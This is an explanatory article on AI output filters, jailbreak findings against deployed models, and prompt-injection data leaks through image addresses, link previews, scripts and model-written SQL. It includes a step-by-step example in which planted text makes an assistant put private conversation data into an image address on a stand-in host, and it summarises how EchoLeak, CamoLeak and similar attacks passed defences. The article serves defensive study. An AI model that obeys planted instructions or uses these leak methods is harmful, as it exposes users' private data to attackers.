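Cunningham and colleagues report that their final system uses 40 times less compute than the exchange classifier, and it uses about 29 times less than the old design. The vulnerability counts are too low to show which of the three newer systems is hardest to break, and the final one refuses more queries than the other two. The strongest evidence in its favour is therefore its low compute use. Understanding AI's *Anthropic’s Fable is the most locked-down public model we’ve ever seen* reports that Anthropic deployed the newer system in 2026.

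### Open streaming filters

Anthropic keeps its classifiers private, but other developers have released streaming filters. Their main difficulty is finding where the harm begins in a training answer. The developers of Qwen3Guard-Stream generated many continuations from each point in an unsafe answer and looked for the earliest point from which most continuations were unsafe. *NExT-Guard* (2026) presents a method that needs no labels for individual tokens. StreamGuard, the filter in *Predict, Don't React* (2026), forecasts whether an answer will become harmful, which could let the wrapper stop it earlier.

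Lenin and colleagues found that a filter with access to the prompt may ignore the answer. They tested an early version of HaloGuard 2.0 on pairs of answers to the same prompt, one safe and one unsafe, and it handled only 13.9% of the pairs correctly. It failed because about 98% of the unsafe answers in its training data were harmful from the first token, so it could do well in training by judging the prompt alone. Such a filter would block a refusal or a safety warning because the prompt sounded dangerous.

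To correct this, Lenin and colleagues wrote matched pairs of safe and unsafe answers, with about half of the unsafe ones beginning harmlessly. They trained a copy of the filter on these pairs and averaged its weights with the original's. False alarms on six public benchmarks fell by 38%. The F1 score combines the share of flagged answers that are harmful with the share of harmful answers that the filter flags. Its average rose from 72.8 to 83.6, compared with 81.0 for the best version of Qwen3Guard-Stream.

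These scores may somewhat overstate how well the filter works. Lenin and colleagues kept the benchmark texts out of the training data, but used the filter's errors on the same benchmarks to decide what kinds of new examples to write. Even with this advantage, the improved filter missed 30.1% of harmful answers on one benchmark and flagged 27% of safe answers on another. Benchmarks contain many borderline cases, so these rates would probably be lower in ordinary traffic, but they are still far too high for a large product.

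### Hiding which filter blocked a request

McKenzie and colleagues attacked a pipeline they had built from open models. They succeeded on 71% of a set of clearly harmful requests, and on 33% when they developed the attack without access to the pipeline. They had set its thresholds to refuse 15% of harmless queries, far stricter than a commercial product could be. They did not test streaming classifiers, which might be harder to attack in some ways and easier in others.

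McKenzie and colleagues mainly advise developers to hide which component blocked a request. An attacker who knows this can work on one component at a time, much as a user can work out what an exact-match filter blocks by watching how it responds. In 2025, the programming interface for Claude Opus 4, since superseded, showed which component had blocked a request. McKenzie and colleagues suggest having the main model write the refusal even when a classifier triggered it, so that all refusals look alike. They would also run the remaining checks after a request fails one, because a faster refusal reveals that an early stage blocked it. They also advise developers to keep their safeguard models and closely related models private, so that attackers cannot practise on a copy.

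Secrecy can also hurt honest users. When Anthropic released Claude Fable 5 in June 2026, Fortune (2026) reported that, according to the model's safety document, some requests about advanced AI development would go to a less capable model without the user knowing. Researchers objected because they could have mistaken the weaker model's work for Fable 5's. According to Willison's *Anthropic Walks Back Policy That Could Have ‘Sabotaged’ AI Researchers Using Claude*, Anthropic apologised and made the switch visible. A visible switch lets attackers see when they have triggered the classifier, which McKenzie and colleagues want to hide, so the classifier has to withstand people who have that information.

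Government testers still find ways past the strongest safeguards. In February 2026 the UK AI Security Institute (UK AISI) announced an automated technique that produces universal jailbreaks against the best-defended systems. The institute also found universal jailbreaks for cybersecurity tasks in every round of testing before OpenAI released GPT-5.6, some within hours. Penligent's *GPT-5.6 SOL Jailbreaks and Agentic Cyber Risk*, a security vendor's account of OpenAI's safety document, says that OpenAI reproduced and mitigated the specific attacks the institute reported. Safeguards have nevertheless become harder to defeat. UK AISI's *Frontier AI Trends Report* compares two models released six months apart and finds that, for certain kinds of request, experts needed 40 times as much effort to jailbreak one as the other.

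### Results from Claude Fable 5

Fable 5 shows how using classifiers to block broad subjects affects false alarms. Its classifiers cover cybersecurity and biology, and a request that triggers them usually goes to a less capable Claude model. Anthropic's *Claude Fable 5 and Claude Mythos 5* (2026) puts the average rate at less than 5% of sessions, which could mean tens of thousands per million. This figure cannot be compared directly with the earlier test's 500 refusals per million queries, because a session can contain many queries and the earlier filter covered only weapons. Outside testers saw more interruptions. According to *Claude's Benchmark Problems*, an article from the education company DeepLearning.AI, the benchmarking firm Artificial Analysis recorded switches on about 8% of its tasks. Another firm, Vals AI, saw refusals on nearly all biology and cybersecurity questions.

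Even these strict settings did not stop every attack. Amazon researchers got Fable 5 to identify software vulnerabilities and, in one case, to write code demonstrating an exploit. The US government responded with export controls, and Anthropic suspended the model. Anthropic's *Redeploying Fable 5* (2026) announced the model's return on 1 July with a new classifier that blocks the reported technique in over 99% of cases. The new classifier also interrupts harmless coding and debugging work more often. Anthropic found that less capable models could do everything in Amazon's report, so the bypass had not exposed the abilities Anthropic most wanted to restrict. The company had set the original classifier to block many probably harmless requests so that a small failure would release only low-risk material.

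Anthropic later reduced false alarms in biology by changing the rules and retraining. *Improving Fable 5's biology safeguards* (Anthropic, 2026) explains that the launch version blocked almost all biology queries so that the company could release the model sooner. In August, after experts helped Anthropic describe harmless uses in more detail, it replaced the classifier, and biology-related switches to a less capable model fell by about 85% in its tests. Questions about lab results and symptoms now usually get through, but those about virology, toxicology and molecular design still go to the less capable model.

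False alarms are more acceptable when a classifier does not block anything. *Scaling Misuse Detection with Self-Assessment* (Zhang, Xia and colleagues, 2026) describes a method in which Claude answers and then rates the safety of the conversation, including how urgently a person should review it. On Fable 5, these ratings flagged 78% of the conversations that a stronger classifier labeled potentially harmful, and 94% of the high-priority ones, with a false-positive rate of 1%. If the method blocked answers, that rate would mean 10,000 unnecessary refusals per million harmless conversations. The comparison cannot reveal misuse that both the model and the stronger classifier missed.

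### Provoking false alarms on purpose

An attacker can use a filter's mistakes to deny service to someone else. *LLM Safeguard is a Double-Edged Sword* (2024) made safeguards block a victim's legitimate requests, both by planting text in the victim's software and by tampering with training data. Users can find and remove planted text by inspecting their software's configuration files, but first they must realise that the refusals have an outside cause.

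An attacker can also use a shared document to get a user's ordinary request refused. The attacker adds a passage to a document that the office assistant has to summarise, and if the summary repeats enough of that passage, it triggers the output filter. Streaming filters are especially vulnerable because one alarm ends the whole answer. The wrapper could reduce the harm by naming the document that caused the block, so that the user can leave it out and try again.

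*From Shield to Target* (2026) examines a different denial-of-service attack, aimed at guards that write out an analysis before they decide. The attacker supplies text that makes this analysis run for a very long time, which delays the agent and uses up computing capacity. A time limit stops the analysis, but the wrapper must then either let unchecked actions through, which gives the attacker a way around the guard, or block them, which still lets the attacker stop the agent from working. Probes and token-by-token classifiers largely avoid this problem because they produce scores without writing an analysis.

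### What a proof about output filters does and does not establish

Better training may reduce a classifier's errors, but Ball, Gluch and colleagues (2025), in *On the Impossibility of Separating Intelligence from Judgment*, prove that no efficient filter can work in every case. For every language model *M*, there is another model *M*′ with a similar running time whose outputs are harmful under some measure of harm, yet no efficient filter can tell them from the outputs of *M*. This holds even if the filter runs for longer than the model and reads the prompt as well as the answer, as an exchange classifier does.

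The proof assumes that time-lock puzzles exist. These puzzles are quick to create but slow to solve, even with many computers working in parallel. In one type, the solver must find the remainder after squaring a number repeatedly and dividing by *n*, the product of two secret primes. For example, suppose *n* = 77 and the number 2 is squared ten times, giving 2¹⁰²⁴. Someone who knows that 77 = 7 × 11 can use Euler's theorem to replace the exponent 1,024 with its remainder after division by 6 × 10 = 60. That remainder is 4, so the answer is 2⁴ = 16. Anyone else has to do the squarings one after another. With large enough primes and enough squarings, this would take longer than any practical filter could run.

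A language model chooses its tokens partly at random. Ball and colleagues construct *M*′ to replace the random bits with an encrypted message and a puzzle whose solution decrypts the message. Those bits look random to a filter that cannot solve the puzzle, so the text looks like ordinary output from *M*. In the proof, the harm of an output depends on the hidden message. It is measured by a mathematical function that neither the model nor the filter can access while running, and that Ball and colleagues interpret as the output's real-world effect.

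The theorem shows that such a model could exist, but not that any deployed model behaves this way or how often deployed filters fail. Ball and colleagues acknowledge that their models are contrived, but point out that artificial-looking weaknesses in cryptography have later led to real attacks. They also say that an output filter is easy to build when harm is easy to recognise. Someone who wants weapon instructions needs an answer they can read and follow, and a filter can detect that. The theorem is more relevant to outputs whose harm appears only in their consequences, such as a business plan that subtly recommends excluding certain clients. Ball and colleagues conclude more broadly that filters outside a model cannot make it safe. Their proof rules out a filter that works for every possible model, but a filter can still prevent much of the misuse of a particular model.

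## How displaying an answer can leak data or run scripts

An answer that passes every output filter can still do harm when an app displays it. The browser may request an image whose address contains private data, or run part of the answer as a script.

### How an image address carries data out

Suppose someone has planted text in the shared document that the office assistant is summarising, and the user has already discussed a merger with the assistant. The leak then takes four steps.

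1. The planted text directs the model to end its summary with an image and to put a fact from the conversation into the image's address.
2. The model writes the summary, followed by a line of Markdown for an image at an address such as `https://pictures.example/logo.png?q=merger-closes-friday`.
3. The wrapper converts the Markdown to an HTML image tag.
4. The browser requests the image as soon as it reads the tag. The attacker runs the server at that address and finds the request, including the note about the merger, in the server's log.

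The user doesn't have to click anything, and sees nothing odd if the server returns a transparent image. The attack relies on private data, untrusted content and a way to send data out, a combination Willison (2026) calls the "lethal trifecta". Willison considers the way to send data out generally the easiest of the three to remove.

Some products make no attempt to stop data leaking through image addresses. In *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering in RAG Chatbot Frontend* (December 2025), veganmosfet built a chatbot with Dify, an open-source kit, and gave it a PDF containing hidden instructions. The chatbot put the user's name in an image address, and Dify's interface fetched the image because it accepted images from any host by default. The post mentions no fix.

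The flaw was already well known by then. *Bing Chat*, a post on the security researcher's blog Embrace The Red, describes it in Microsoft's chatbot in 2023. Bing Chat could read the web page the user had open, so a comment or advertisement on that page could direct it to leak the rest of the page and a summary of the conversation. The researcher reported the flaw on 8 April, and Microsoft announced a fix on 15 June. At least part of the fix was a content security policy (CSP), which a website sends with a page to limit the hosts from which the browser may load images, scripts and other resources. Bing Chat's new policy allowed images from only a few Bing hosts.

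GitHub Copilot Chat had the same flaw in 2024, which put the user's source code at risk. Willison reports in *GitHub Copilot Chat* that GitHub fixed it by no longer displaying Markdown images from untrusted domains. Both companies therefore relied on a list of approved hosts.

### EchoLeak and the controls it passed

Microsoft 365 Copilot answers employees' questions by retrieving relevant passages from their email, files and chats. In January 2025, researchers at Aim Labs found that an outsider could steal that data by sending an employee an email. In *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability*, Ravia (2025) explains how the attack got past several controls.

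The email first had to reach the model. Copilot retrieves text in passages, so the researchers wrote a long email with sections on many common office topics, which made it likely that one would match an employee's next question. A classifier screened incoming text for prompt injection, but the email never mentioned AI and addressed its instructions to the human recipient. Ordinary business email often contains such instructions, so a classifier strict enough to catch this email would probably also flag a lot of legitimate mail.

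Copilot then wrote an answer with private data in an address. Microsoft had anticipated this and used code to remove outside links and images from answers, but the code recognised only the most common Markdown notation, in which the address directly follows the link text. Markdown also lets a writer put a short label there and give the address for that label elsewhere. The redaction code did not recognise this form but the renderer did, a mismatch called a parser differential. Converting the answer to HTML first and then checking every address is more reliable, because both notations produce the same HTML tags.

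The browser's CSP still blocked requests to the attacker's own server. However, Microsoft's list of approved hosts had dozens of entries, and one covered every host under `teams.microsoft.com`. A service there would fetch any address that a visitor supplied. The browser requested an image from Teams, as the policy allowed. The Teams server then requested the attacker's address with the private data in it, which the CSP could not block because it controls only requests made by the browser.

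Copilot normally names the sources of an answer, which might have alerted the employee. The email included a request that its recipient never refer to it, and Copilot left the email out of its sources.

Microsoft fixed the flaw on its own servers in May 2025, and Aim Labs published the attack on 11 June. Microsoft told the researchers that no customers had been affected. *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) calls the attack the first known case of prompt injection causing concrete data exfiltration in a production system, but Bing Chat had leaked data in the same way two years earlier. The new attack differed in that the victim only had to ask Copilot an unrelated question, without opening the attacker's page or document.

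Reddy and Gujral recommend marking outside text with tags so that the model treats it as data. This may help, but similar tags only delayed the attacker in the experiment by Deep and colleagues. Reddy and Gujral also report that Microsoft now strips reference-style links and embedded images from outside content. That removes ready-made links, but the outside text in the Bing Chat demonstration described the image in words and had the model assemble it. The wrapper therefore also has to check the model's answer.

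### Approved hosts that pass data on

A year after EchoLeak, Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) described another leak from Microsoft 365 Copilot, through its Enterprise Search page. The attacker sent the victim a link to the genuine Microsoft site, with instructions for Copilot in the part of the address meant for a search query. One click made Copilot search the victim's mailbox and write an image tag containing an email's title, which might include a login code.

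The wrapper converted such tags to harmless text only after Copilot had finished writing, so the browser read the tag and requested the image while the answer was still streaming. The CSP allowed requests to Bing, whose image search fetched any image address it received. Bing's server therefore sent the email title to the attacker, much as Teams had done in EchoLeak. Bing was already on the list of approved hosts that Ravia published in 2025. Microsoft rated the flaw (CVE-2026-42824) critical and has fixed it.

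An approved host can also leak data without forwarding anything. The email product Superhuman allowed images from `docs.google.com`, where Google Forms saves data submitted in a URL. An attacker could create a form and read the victim's email in its responses. Superhuman issued a fix in January 2026. According to Willison, Salesforce's Agentforce still approved a domain whose registration had expired, and in 2025 researchers bought the domain and received customer data there. Salesforce corrected its list of approved domains and added a check on the links its agent writes.

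ChatGPT's list had a similar gap. Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* reports that OpenAI approved `windows.net`, a domain on which anyone can rent storage from Microsoft and inspect the log of incoming requests. The researcher reported this in October 2024, and around August 2025 OpenAI added protections that stopped the attack.

Before approving a host, a developer has to know whether outsiders can store data there, read its logs or make it fetch other addresses, and the answers can change whenever the host's owner adds a feature. A browser checks every redirect of an image request against the CSP, but a wrapper that fetches pages for an agent may check only the first address.

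### What a choice among fixed addresses reveals

A stricter rule approves complete addresses instead of hosts, so the model cannot add anything to them. GitHub had such a rule in 2025. Its CSP blocked images from outside GitHub, but project pages could show them through a proxy called Camo. When someone saves a page with an outside image, GitHub replaces the image's address with one on the proxy and adds a signature, which is a code computed from the original address with a secret key. Camo fetches the image only if the signature is valid. A language model does not have the key, so it cannot produce a valid address containing a secret.

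Legit Security's *CamoLeak* shows how a researcher got around this in Copilot Chat. The researcher obtained a signed address for each letter and symbol in advance, then put the list in a hidden comment in the description of a pull request (a proposed change to a project's code), where people reading the page would not see it. When another user asked Copilot about the pull request, Copilot spelled out private text as a row of invisible images, and each image request revealed one character to the researcher's server. Browsers normally fetch a repeated image only once, so the researcher also had Copilot add a random number to each address.

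Copilot had the same access as the user who asked the question. In one demonstration, it leaked the description of an unpatched vulnerability from a private project. GitHub fixed the flaw on 14 August 2025 by turning off images in Copilot Chat.

The signatures worked as designed, but the model could still choose which signed address to use. With *n* signed addresses, one request can send any of *n* messages, so it carries log₂ *n* bits, where one bit is the answer to a yes-or-no question. With four addresses, a request carries two bits, because 2² = 4. A series of *r* requests can send any of *n*ʳ messages, so it carries *r* × log₂ *n* bits.

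A random 16-character code made of capital letters and digits has 36¹⁶ possible values, so it carries about 82.7 bits of information. The number of requests needed to send the code depends on the number of approved addresses.

| Approved addresses | Bits per request | Requests needed for the code |
|---|---|---|
| 2 | 1 | 83 |
| 36 | 5.17 | 16 |
| 1,024 | 10 | 9 |

A shorter list of approved addresses slows the leak but does not stop it. Even a single address leaks one bit if the model's output determines whether it is requested.

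### Approving only addresses that are already public

OpenAI now approves exact addresses for ChatGPT as well. *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link*, which OpenAI published in January 2026, describes an index of public web addresses that a crawler collects without access to any user's conversations. ChatGPT can automatically load an address that is in the index. Otherwise, it looks for another source or shows the user a warning. An address that the model composes from someone's private data is very unlikely to be in the index.

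The attacker can still publish one page per character and wait for the crawler to find them. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* notes that OpenAI acknowledges this weakness, and that anyone with a large website probably already has 36 suitable pages in the index. The post suggests not letting the agent visit the same address twice in one session.

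Blocking repeated requests to the same address would not stop the leak. With 36 addresses, the attacker still learns which ones the agent requested, which can carry 36 bits. A four-digit PIN needs only 13.3. If the requests also arrive in the intended order, the 36! possible sequences that use every address once can carry about 138 bits, more than enough for the 16-character code. Limiting the number of requests is more effective. Three requests to 36 addresses carry less than 16 bits, though that would still be enough for the PIN.

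In July 2026, Ayush Paul demonstrated a leak of this kind in Claude's tool for reading web pages. The tool could open addresses typed by the user, returned by a search or found on a page it had already opened. Paul built a website with a link for each letter and got Claude to spell out information about the user by following the links. Willison recounts that Claude revealed the user's name, home city and employer. Anthropic said it had already found the problem itself, and it no longer lets the tool follow links on the pages it opens.

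An agent's choice of links can reveal private information even when no one has told it to leak anything. In *Actions Speak Louder than Words*, Liang, Deng and colleagues (2026) gave research agents pages of links on different subjects and watched which ones they opened. In one example, an agent investigates why influenza can be deadlier than COVID-19 in children. It chooses biological mechanisms rather than clinical outcomes, then immune response rather than pathogenesis, and these two choices reveal part of the user's question.

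With four links on a page, the agents made a visible choice in 98.7% of trials, and in 93.8% of those the choice correctly identified what the agent was looking for. Liang and colleagues then built a system that used a series of increasingly specific pages of links. They tested it on four agents and three models with 500 questions from StackExchange. It recovered the concepts in each question with an average F1 score of 0.89, using about 6.5 pages of links per question. The attacker must be able to put a link to the probing site on a page that the agent visits.

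Four existing defenses lowered the score by no more than 0.03. They try to detect planted instructions, actions unrelated to the task or private data in outgoing requests, but this attack may involve none of these. Liang and colleagues propose that the agent download a fixed number of pages, chosen without using the user's private information, and then select what it needs from the local copies. This reduced the score to 0.39. The same principle would have protected Copilot Chat's images, because if the wrapper fetches every image in a pull request before the model reads any of it, the requests cannot depend on private data.

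### Logs, messages and previews

A blocked answer may still be stored, and opening the stored copy can leak data it contains. PromptArmor's *OpenAI API Logs* demonstrates this with a mock banking application that checks customers' identities. Text planted in one of the application's sources caused the model to write an image address that included the customer's personal and financial details. A second model, used as an output filter, flagged the answer, so the application did not display it. A developer then opened the conversation in OpenAI's log viewer to investigate. The viewer displayed the answer as Markdown, and the developer's browser requested the image, which sent the customer's data to the attacker.

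The application's own defenses did not protect the log viewer. A CSP applies only to the site that sends it, and an application that shows answers as plain text cannot control how OpenAI's website shows them. A sanitiser could even make a developer more likely to open the dangerous conversation. If it removes an image and leaves a strangely empty answer, the user may give the answer a thumbs-down, and a developer may then open the original in the log.

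PromptArmor reported the flaw in November 2025. Bugcrowd, which screens such reports for OpenAI, closed the case as "Not applicable" on 4 December. OpenAI had not seen the report, and reopened the case on 22 January 2026 after PromptArmor published its findings. OpenAI confirmed the flaw and said it was working on a fix. PromptArmor does not say in its account when OpenAI finished the fix.

OpenAI had already built a check on image addresses for ChatGPT but had not applied it in the log viewer. Embrace The Red had also found it missing earlier from the ChatGPT apps for macOS and iOS. A company can avoid such gaps by removing external images before it stores an answer, or by having all its products use the same display code.

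Messaging apps can leak data through link previews. Slack, Telegram and similar apps fetch links in messages to show each page's title and a picture. If a chatbot has written private data into a link's address, fetching the preview sends that data to the server at that address without a click. Willison's *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* (2024) described the risk in Slack and Discord, and noted that a program posting to Slack can turn off previews for its own messages. In February 2026, PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* showed that OpenClaw, a popular agent, was vulnerable by default when used through Telegram. Users can disable previews in OpenClaw's configuration file. A browser's CSP would not help, because the messaging service may fetch the preview from its own servers.

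Displaying an email can also leak data. Microsoft's Copilot Cowork, an agent for office work, could send messages to the user's own inbox without approval, presumably because no outsider would receive them. But the messages could contain images from outside servers, and the image addresses could contain links that let anyone download the user's files. Opening such a message was enough to leak the files. Willison, who wrote about the flaw in May 2026, does not mention a fix.

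### Links that need a click, and reports that vendors declined

Even when images are blocked, an ordinary link can leak data if the user clicks it. *Trust No AI* (2024) describes an attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot that put data from the victim's inbox into a link as invisible characters. Microsoft fixed the vulnerability in July 2024. Amazon stopped displaying links in Amazon Q for Business to address a similar problem.

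Google has not gone that far. Gemini removes outside images and any links that Google's Safe Browsing service lists as malicious, but an attacker can register a new domain that isn't listed yet. Checkmarx's *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents* says Google closed a report about this in October 2025 as "Won't Fix (Infeasible)". Removing all outside links would make an assistant much less useful for research. OpenAI's warning for unfamiliar addresses is a compromise, but few users will be able to judge a long encoded address, and OpenAI points out that frequent warnings train people to click through.

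Microsoft's response to another report from Checkmarx is harder to defend. The reported attack involved an image and needed no click on a link. In the demonstration, Copilot Chat read an article containing planted text and leaked a secret key from a developer's computer. Microsoft closed the report in November 2025 without a fix, saying the behaviour "does not meet our classification for a security vulnerability". It said the attack required several non-default actions, did not work reliably and triggered warnings. Those are reasons to rate the flaw as less severe, but GitHub had fixed a very similar leak in 2024.

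The same month, a researcher reported an image leak in Antigravity, Google's programming tool, and said that Google had classed it as intended behaviour. Google's page for bug hunters listed data exfiltration from Antigravity among the known issues it was working to fix, which made new reports ineligible for a reward. In 2024, xAI closed reports of leaks from its chatbot Grok as "Informational". These labels mainly determine whether a vendor tracks or pays for a report, and the log viewer case shows that a closed report can still describe a real leak.

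### When an answer runs as a script

A wrapper that pastes an answer unchanged into a page is open to cross-site scripting. A `<` in the answer marks the start of an HTML tag, and some tags contain code. The browser runs that code with the same rights as the site's own scripts, so the code may be able to read the token that keeps the user signed in.

DeepSeek's chatbot had this flaw, which DeepSeek has since patched. *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation* (Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian, 2026) explains that the prompt contained an encoded script, the model decoded it, and the chat page ran it. The script could read the user's session token. If an application saves the model's answer elsewhere, such as in a support ticket, the script also runs in the browser of any employee who opens it.

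The basic fix is to encode the answer just before inserting it into the page. In HTML, `&lt;` stands for a visible `<`, so a browser that receives `&lt;b&gt;` displays the characters `<b>` instead of starting bold text. Code that runs in the browser can get the same result by inserting the answer through `textContent`, which treats it as text, rather than `innerHTML`, which parses it as HTML. *Shifting from Injection to Interaction* also recommends having the model answer in a fixed format such as JSON. This helps the application separate the parts of an answer, but a JSON string can still contain a script, so the application must encode each part before displaying it.

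The right encoding depends on where the text goes. For example, a link's address can start with a prefix that makes the browser run code instead of opening a page, and it may contain none of the characters that HTML encoding changes. The wrapper should therefore allow only addresses with expected prefixes, such as `https:`.

Encoding the whole answer also removes its formatting. Products that show headings and links usually convert the Markdown to HTML and pass it through a sanitiser, which keeps only approved tags and attributes. The sanitiser has to run after the conversion, because the conversion can create new tags. A sanitiser that removes only scripts will leave ordinary image tags in place, so the wrapper also needs a rule for image addresses.

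When a system streams an answer, the browser can act on part of it before protections apply. In SearchLeak, the protection took effect only after the browser had requested the image. Similarly, in 2025, text streamed by GitLab Duo, a programming assistant, could bypass the filter against scripts. Willison reports that GitLab's fix limits links and images to trusted domains. The wrapper can prevent both problems by sanitising the partial answer every time it updates the page.

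If the sanitiser misses a script, a content security policy (CSP) may still stop it from running. A CSP can block all scripts written directly into the page except those the developer has marked with a random value, which changes each time the page loads. Many sites weaken this protection by allowing all scripts written into the page so that older code keeps working. Another browser feature, Trusted Types, rejects text passed to `innerHTML` and similar features unless it has gone through a sanitiser the developer has approved. This can catch places where a programmer forgot to sanitise the text, but it cannot correct a sanitiser that allows the wrong tags.

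## When an application runs the model's answer as code or a query

Some applications run the model's output on purpose, whereas a script in a chat answer runs because a developer forgot to neutralise it. These applications have the model write a database query, a short program or a web address, and pass the result to software that executes it. This is useful because a database, for example, adds up a million sales more reliably than a language model does. But anyone who can influence the model's input may also influence what runs on the company's servers.

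### A sales assistant that writes its own queries

Suppose a company connects an assistant to its sales database. The `sales` table holds the date, region, amount and salesperson for each sale, and the `employees` table holds names and salaries. Staff ask questions in English, and the model translates them into SQL, the standard language for querying databases.

Pedro, Carreira and colleagues (2023), in *From Prompt Injections to SQL Injection Attacks*, describe how LangChain, a popular kit for building such applications, handled a question. The wrapper gave the model the names of the tables and columns, followed by the question, and the model wrote a query. The wrapper ran the query and added the result to the model's input, and the model then wrote an answer. For "Which region sold the most in October?", the query might be:

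```
SELECT region, SUM(amount) AS total
FROM sales
WHERE sold_on >= '2026-10-01' AND sold_on < '2026-11-01'
GROUP BY region
ORDER BY total DESC
LIMIT 1;
```

Nothing in this sequence checks whether the user is allowed to see the data. If someone asks for everyone's salary, the model can write a valid query on `employees`, and the database will run it if the assistant's account has access to that table.

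### Why parameters do not help

In a parameterised query, the usual protection against SQL injection, the programmer writes the query in advance and leaves a gap for the user's value:

```
SELECT SUM(amount) FROM sales WHERE region = $1;
```

If a visitor types SQL into the region box, the database looks for a region with that name. The programmer controls the rest of the query, including which table it reads, so the visitor controls only that one value.

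When the model writes the whole query, no part of it is fixed, so the query could still read the salaries even if the wrapper sent every date and name as a parameter. *Reimagining Text-to-SQL* (2026), a survey from November, nevertheless lists parameterised queries among its countermeasures for malicious generated SQL. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian say more precisely that an application still needs them when it inserts a user's value into a query, but that they are insufficient when the model generates the query's structure.

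Even when a query is fixed, the application needs to check who is asking. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian describe a shop's chatbot that took an order number from a customer's message and looked it up. The customer controlled only the number, but the software never checked whose order it was, so the chatbot gave out other people's email and delivery addresses.

### What happens when the rules are in the prompt

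Pedro and colleagues tested their attacks on a job-listing site they built with LangChain 0.0.189 and GPT-3.5. The site's database account could read and change everything. With LangChain's default prompt, a user could delete tables, alter records or read everyone's details just by asking. Each of these attacks worked in all 30 attempts. The researchers then added rules to the prompt telling the model to only read data and to return only the current user's rows. The rules stopped direct requests, but more elaborate prompts got past them every time.

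An attacker could also plant instructions in a job advert stored in the database, and these reached the model when another user asked about jobs. One such advert made the model change a user's email address, which is enough to take over an account, and then answer the original question as if nothing had happened. The attack required LangChain's agent version, which could run several queries for one question. Pedro and colleagues built their defences as extensions to LangChain and report no change to LangChain itself.

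Models have since become harder to fool. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian (2026) tried similar techniques on newer models without success. But a model can break a rule in its prompt even when nobody is attacking it. Fei and Yang (2026), in *Benchmarking Text-to-SQL under Role-Based Access Control*, took three public collections of database questions, created plausible job roles for each database, and gave the model the role's permissions along with each question. GPT-5 wrote a forbidden query in 2.6% of cases on the easiest collection, 10.5% on the next and 17.8% on the hardest. Claude Sonnet 4.5 did so in 4.9%, 7.7% and 13.3%. Newer models have replaced both and may do better, but violations became more common as queries had to combine more tables, and those are the queries people most want help with.

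### Read-only accounts and restricted views

The database can enforce these rules itself. Every program connects to it through an account, and an administrator chooses what that account may do with each table. If the sales assistant's account may only read `sales`, the database will reject a deletion or a query on salaries, whoever caused the model to write it. In tests by Pedro and colleagues, a read-only account stopped the attacks that deleted or altered records, including the one that changed an email address. It did not stop users from reading each other's data, because the permission covered the whole table.

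A view can narrow this down to particular rows. It is a saved query that other queries can use as if it were a table. Google Cloud offers a kind of view in its AlloyDB database service that takes the user's identity as a parameter, and recommends it for queries translated from natural language. For the sales assistant, it might look like this:

```
CREATE VIEW my_sales WITH (security_barrier) AS
SELECT sold_on, region, amount
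FROM sales
WHERE rep_id = $@app_user_id;
```

The assistant's account can read the view `my_sales` but not the `sales` table, so if the model writes a query that adds up every sale, a salesperson gets only the total of their own. The view's `security_barrier` option keeps functions in the model's query from receiving rows before the view has filtered them. The wrapper takes the user's identity from their login, and Google's *alloydb-ai-nl Tool* recommends supplying it in a way that hides it from the model. A user who persuades the model that they are someone else therefore still sees only their own sales.

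Pedro and colleagues got a similar result on an ordinary database by rewriting the model's query to replace each mention of a sensitive table with a subquery for the current user's rows. This took about 2 milliseconds. Their other main defence, a second model that checked the results for planted instructions, took about 0.4 seconds and could be fooled. Rewriting fails if the rewriter misses any mention of the table, so the rewriter must parse the query exactly as the database will.

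The database account that runs the model's queries should itself be read-only, because a query may be able to undo a read-only setting that applies just to the transaction. Datadog Security Labs' *MCP vulnerability case study* (2025) examined Anthropic's reference server for connecting models to PostgreSQL, a widely used database. The server ran the model's query inside a read-only transaction, but it accepted several statements at once, so a query could end the transaction and then delete data. The fix sends each query as a prepared statement, a mechanism normally used for parameters, because a prepared statement cannot contain a second command.

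Anthropic fixed its source code in May 2025 and archived the project, but by August it had not released the fixed package, and people were still downloading the vulnerable one about 21,000 times a week. A version maintained by Zed Industries has the fix. *SQL Query Engine* (2026) calls a read-only setting in its own database driver a "hard boundary", which is true only if the query cannot change that setting.

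A restricted account leaves some problems unsolved. Datadog Security Labs found that the PostgreSQL server reused connections, so one user's query could set a very short time limit that made other users' queries fail. The repaired version closes the connection after each call. Permissions also do not prevent inference. Fei and Yang point out that a user who may see hourly wages and hours worked can calculate a salary that the user is not permitted to see. A model with read-only access may still leak what it reads through another tool. Discussing the Supabase database service in 2025, Willison noted that read-only mode stops an attacker from extracting data by having the model write it to the database, but he still considered the remaining risk enormous.

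Database permissions make the application less useful when they cause reasonable questions to fail. In an example from Fei and Yang, a sales analyst asks which departments bring in the most revenue per employee. The model writes a correct query that uses the employee table, but the database returns an error because the analyst has no permission to read that table. The data is safe, but the analyst has no answer and may not know why. Showing the model only the tables that the analyst can use should avoid some of these failures, though Fei and Yang found that it was not enough by itself.

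### Checking generated code before it runs

Many applications check the model's code before running it and reject anything they consider dangerous. The crudest checks examine the code only as text. OSV's *CVE-2025-59333* describes a database server whose read-only mode tested whether the query started with `SELECT`, the SQL command for reading, so a query could pass with a second, unchecked statement after the first.

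Better checks parse the code, but they often rely on a list of forbidden features, which is hard to complete. Microsoft (2026) found this problem in Semantic Kernel, its own kit for building agents. In the demonstration, the model supplied a city name for a hotel search. Semantic Kernel pasted the name into a line of Python and ran it with `eval`, a function that executes text as code, so code supplied as a city name could run.

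The developers had expected this. Their check parsed the line into a tree of its parts, rejected it if it contained certain names, and ran the rest without Python's built-in functions. But Python code can reach the same function in many ways, and the researchers found one that used only names missing from the list. Version 1.39.4 of the Python package fixes the flaw by permitting comparisons, arithmetic, simple logic and a few safe functions, and rejecting nearly everything else. A hotel filter needs little more than that, so the restriction barely limits it.

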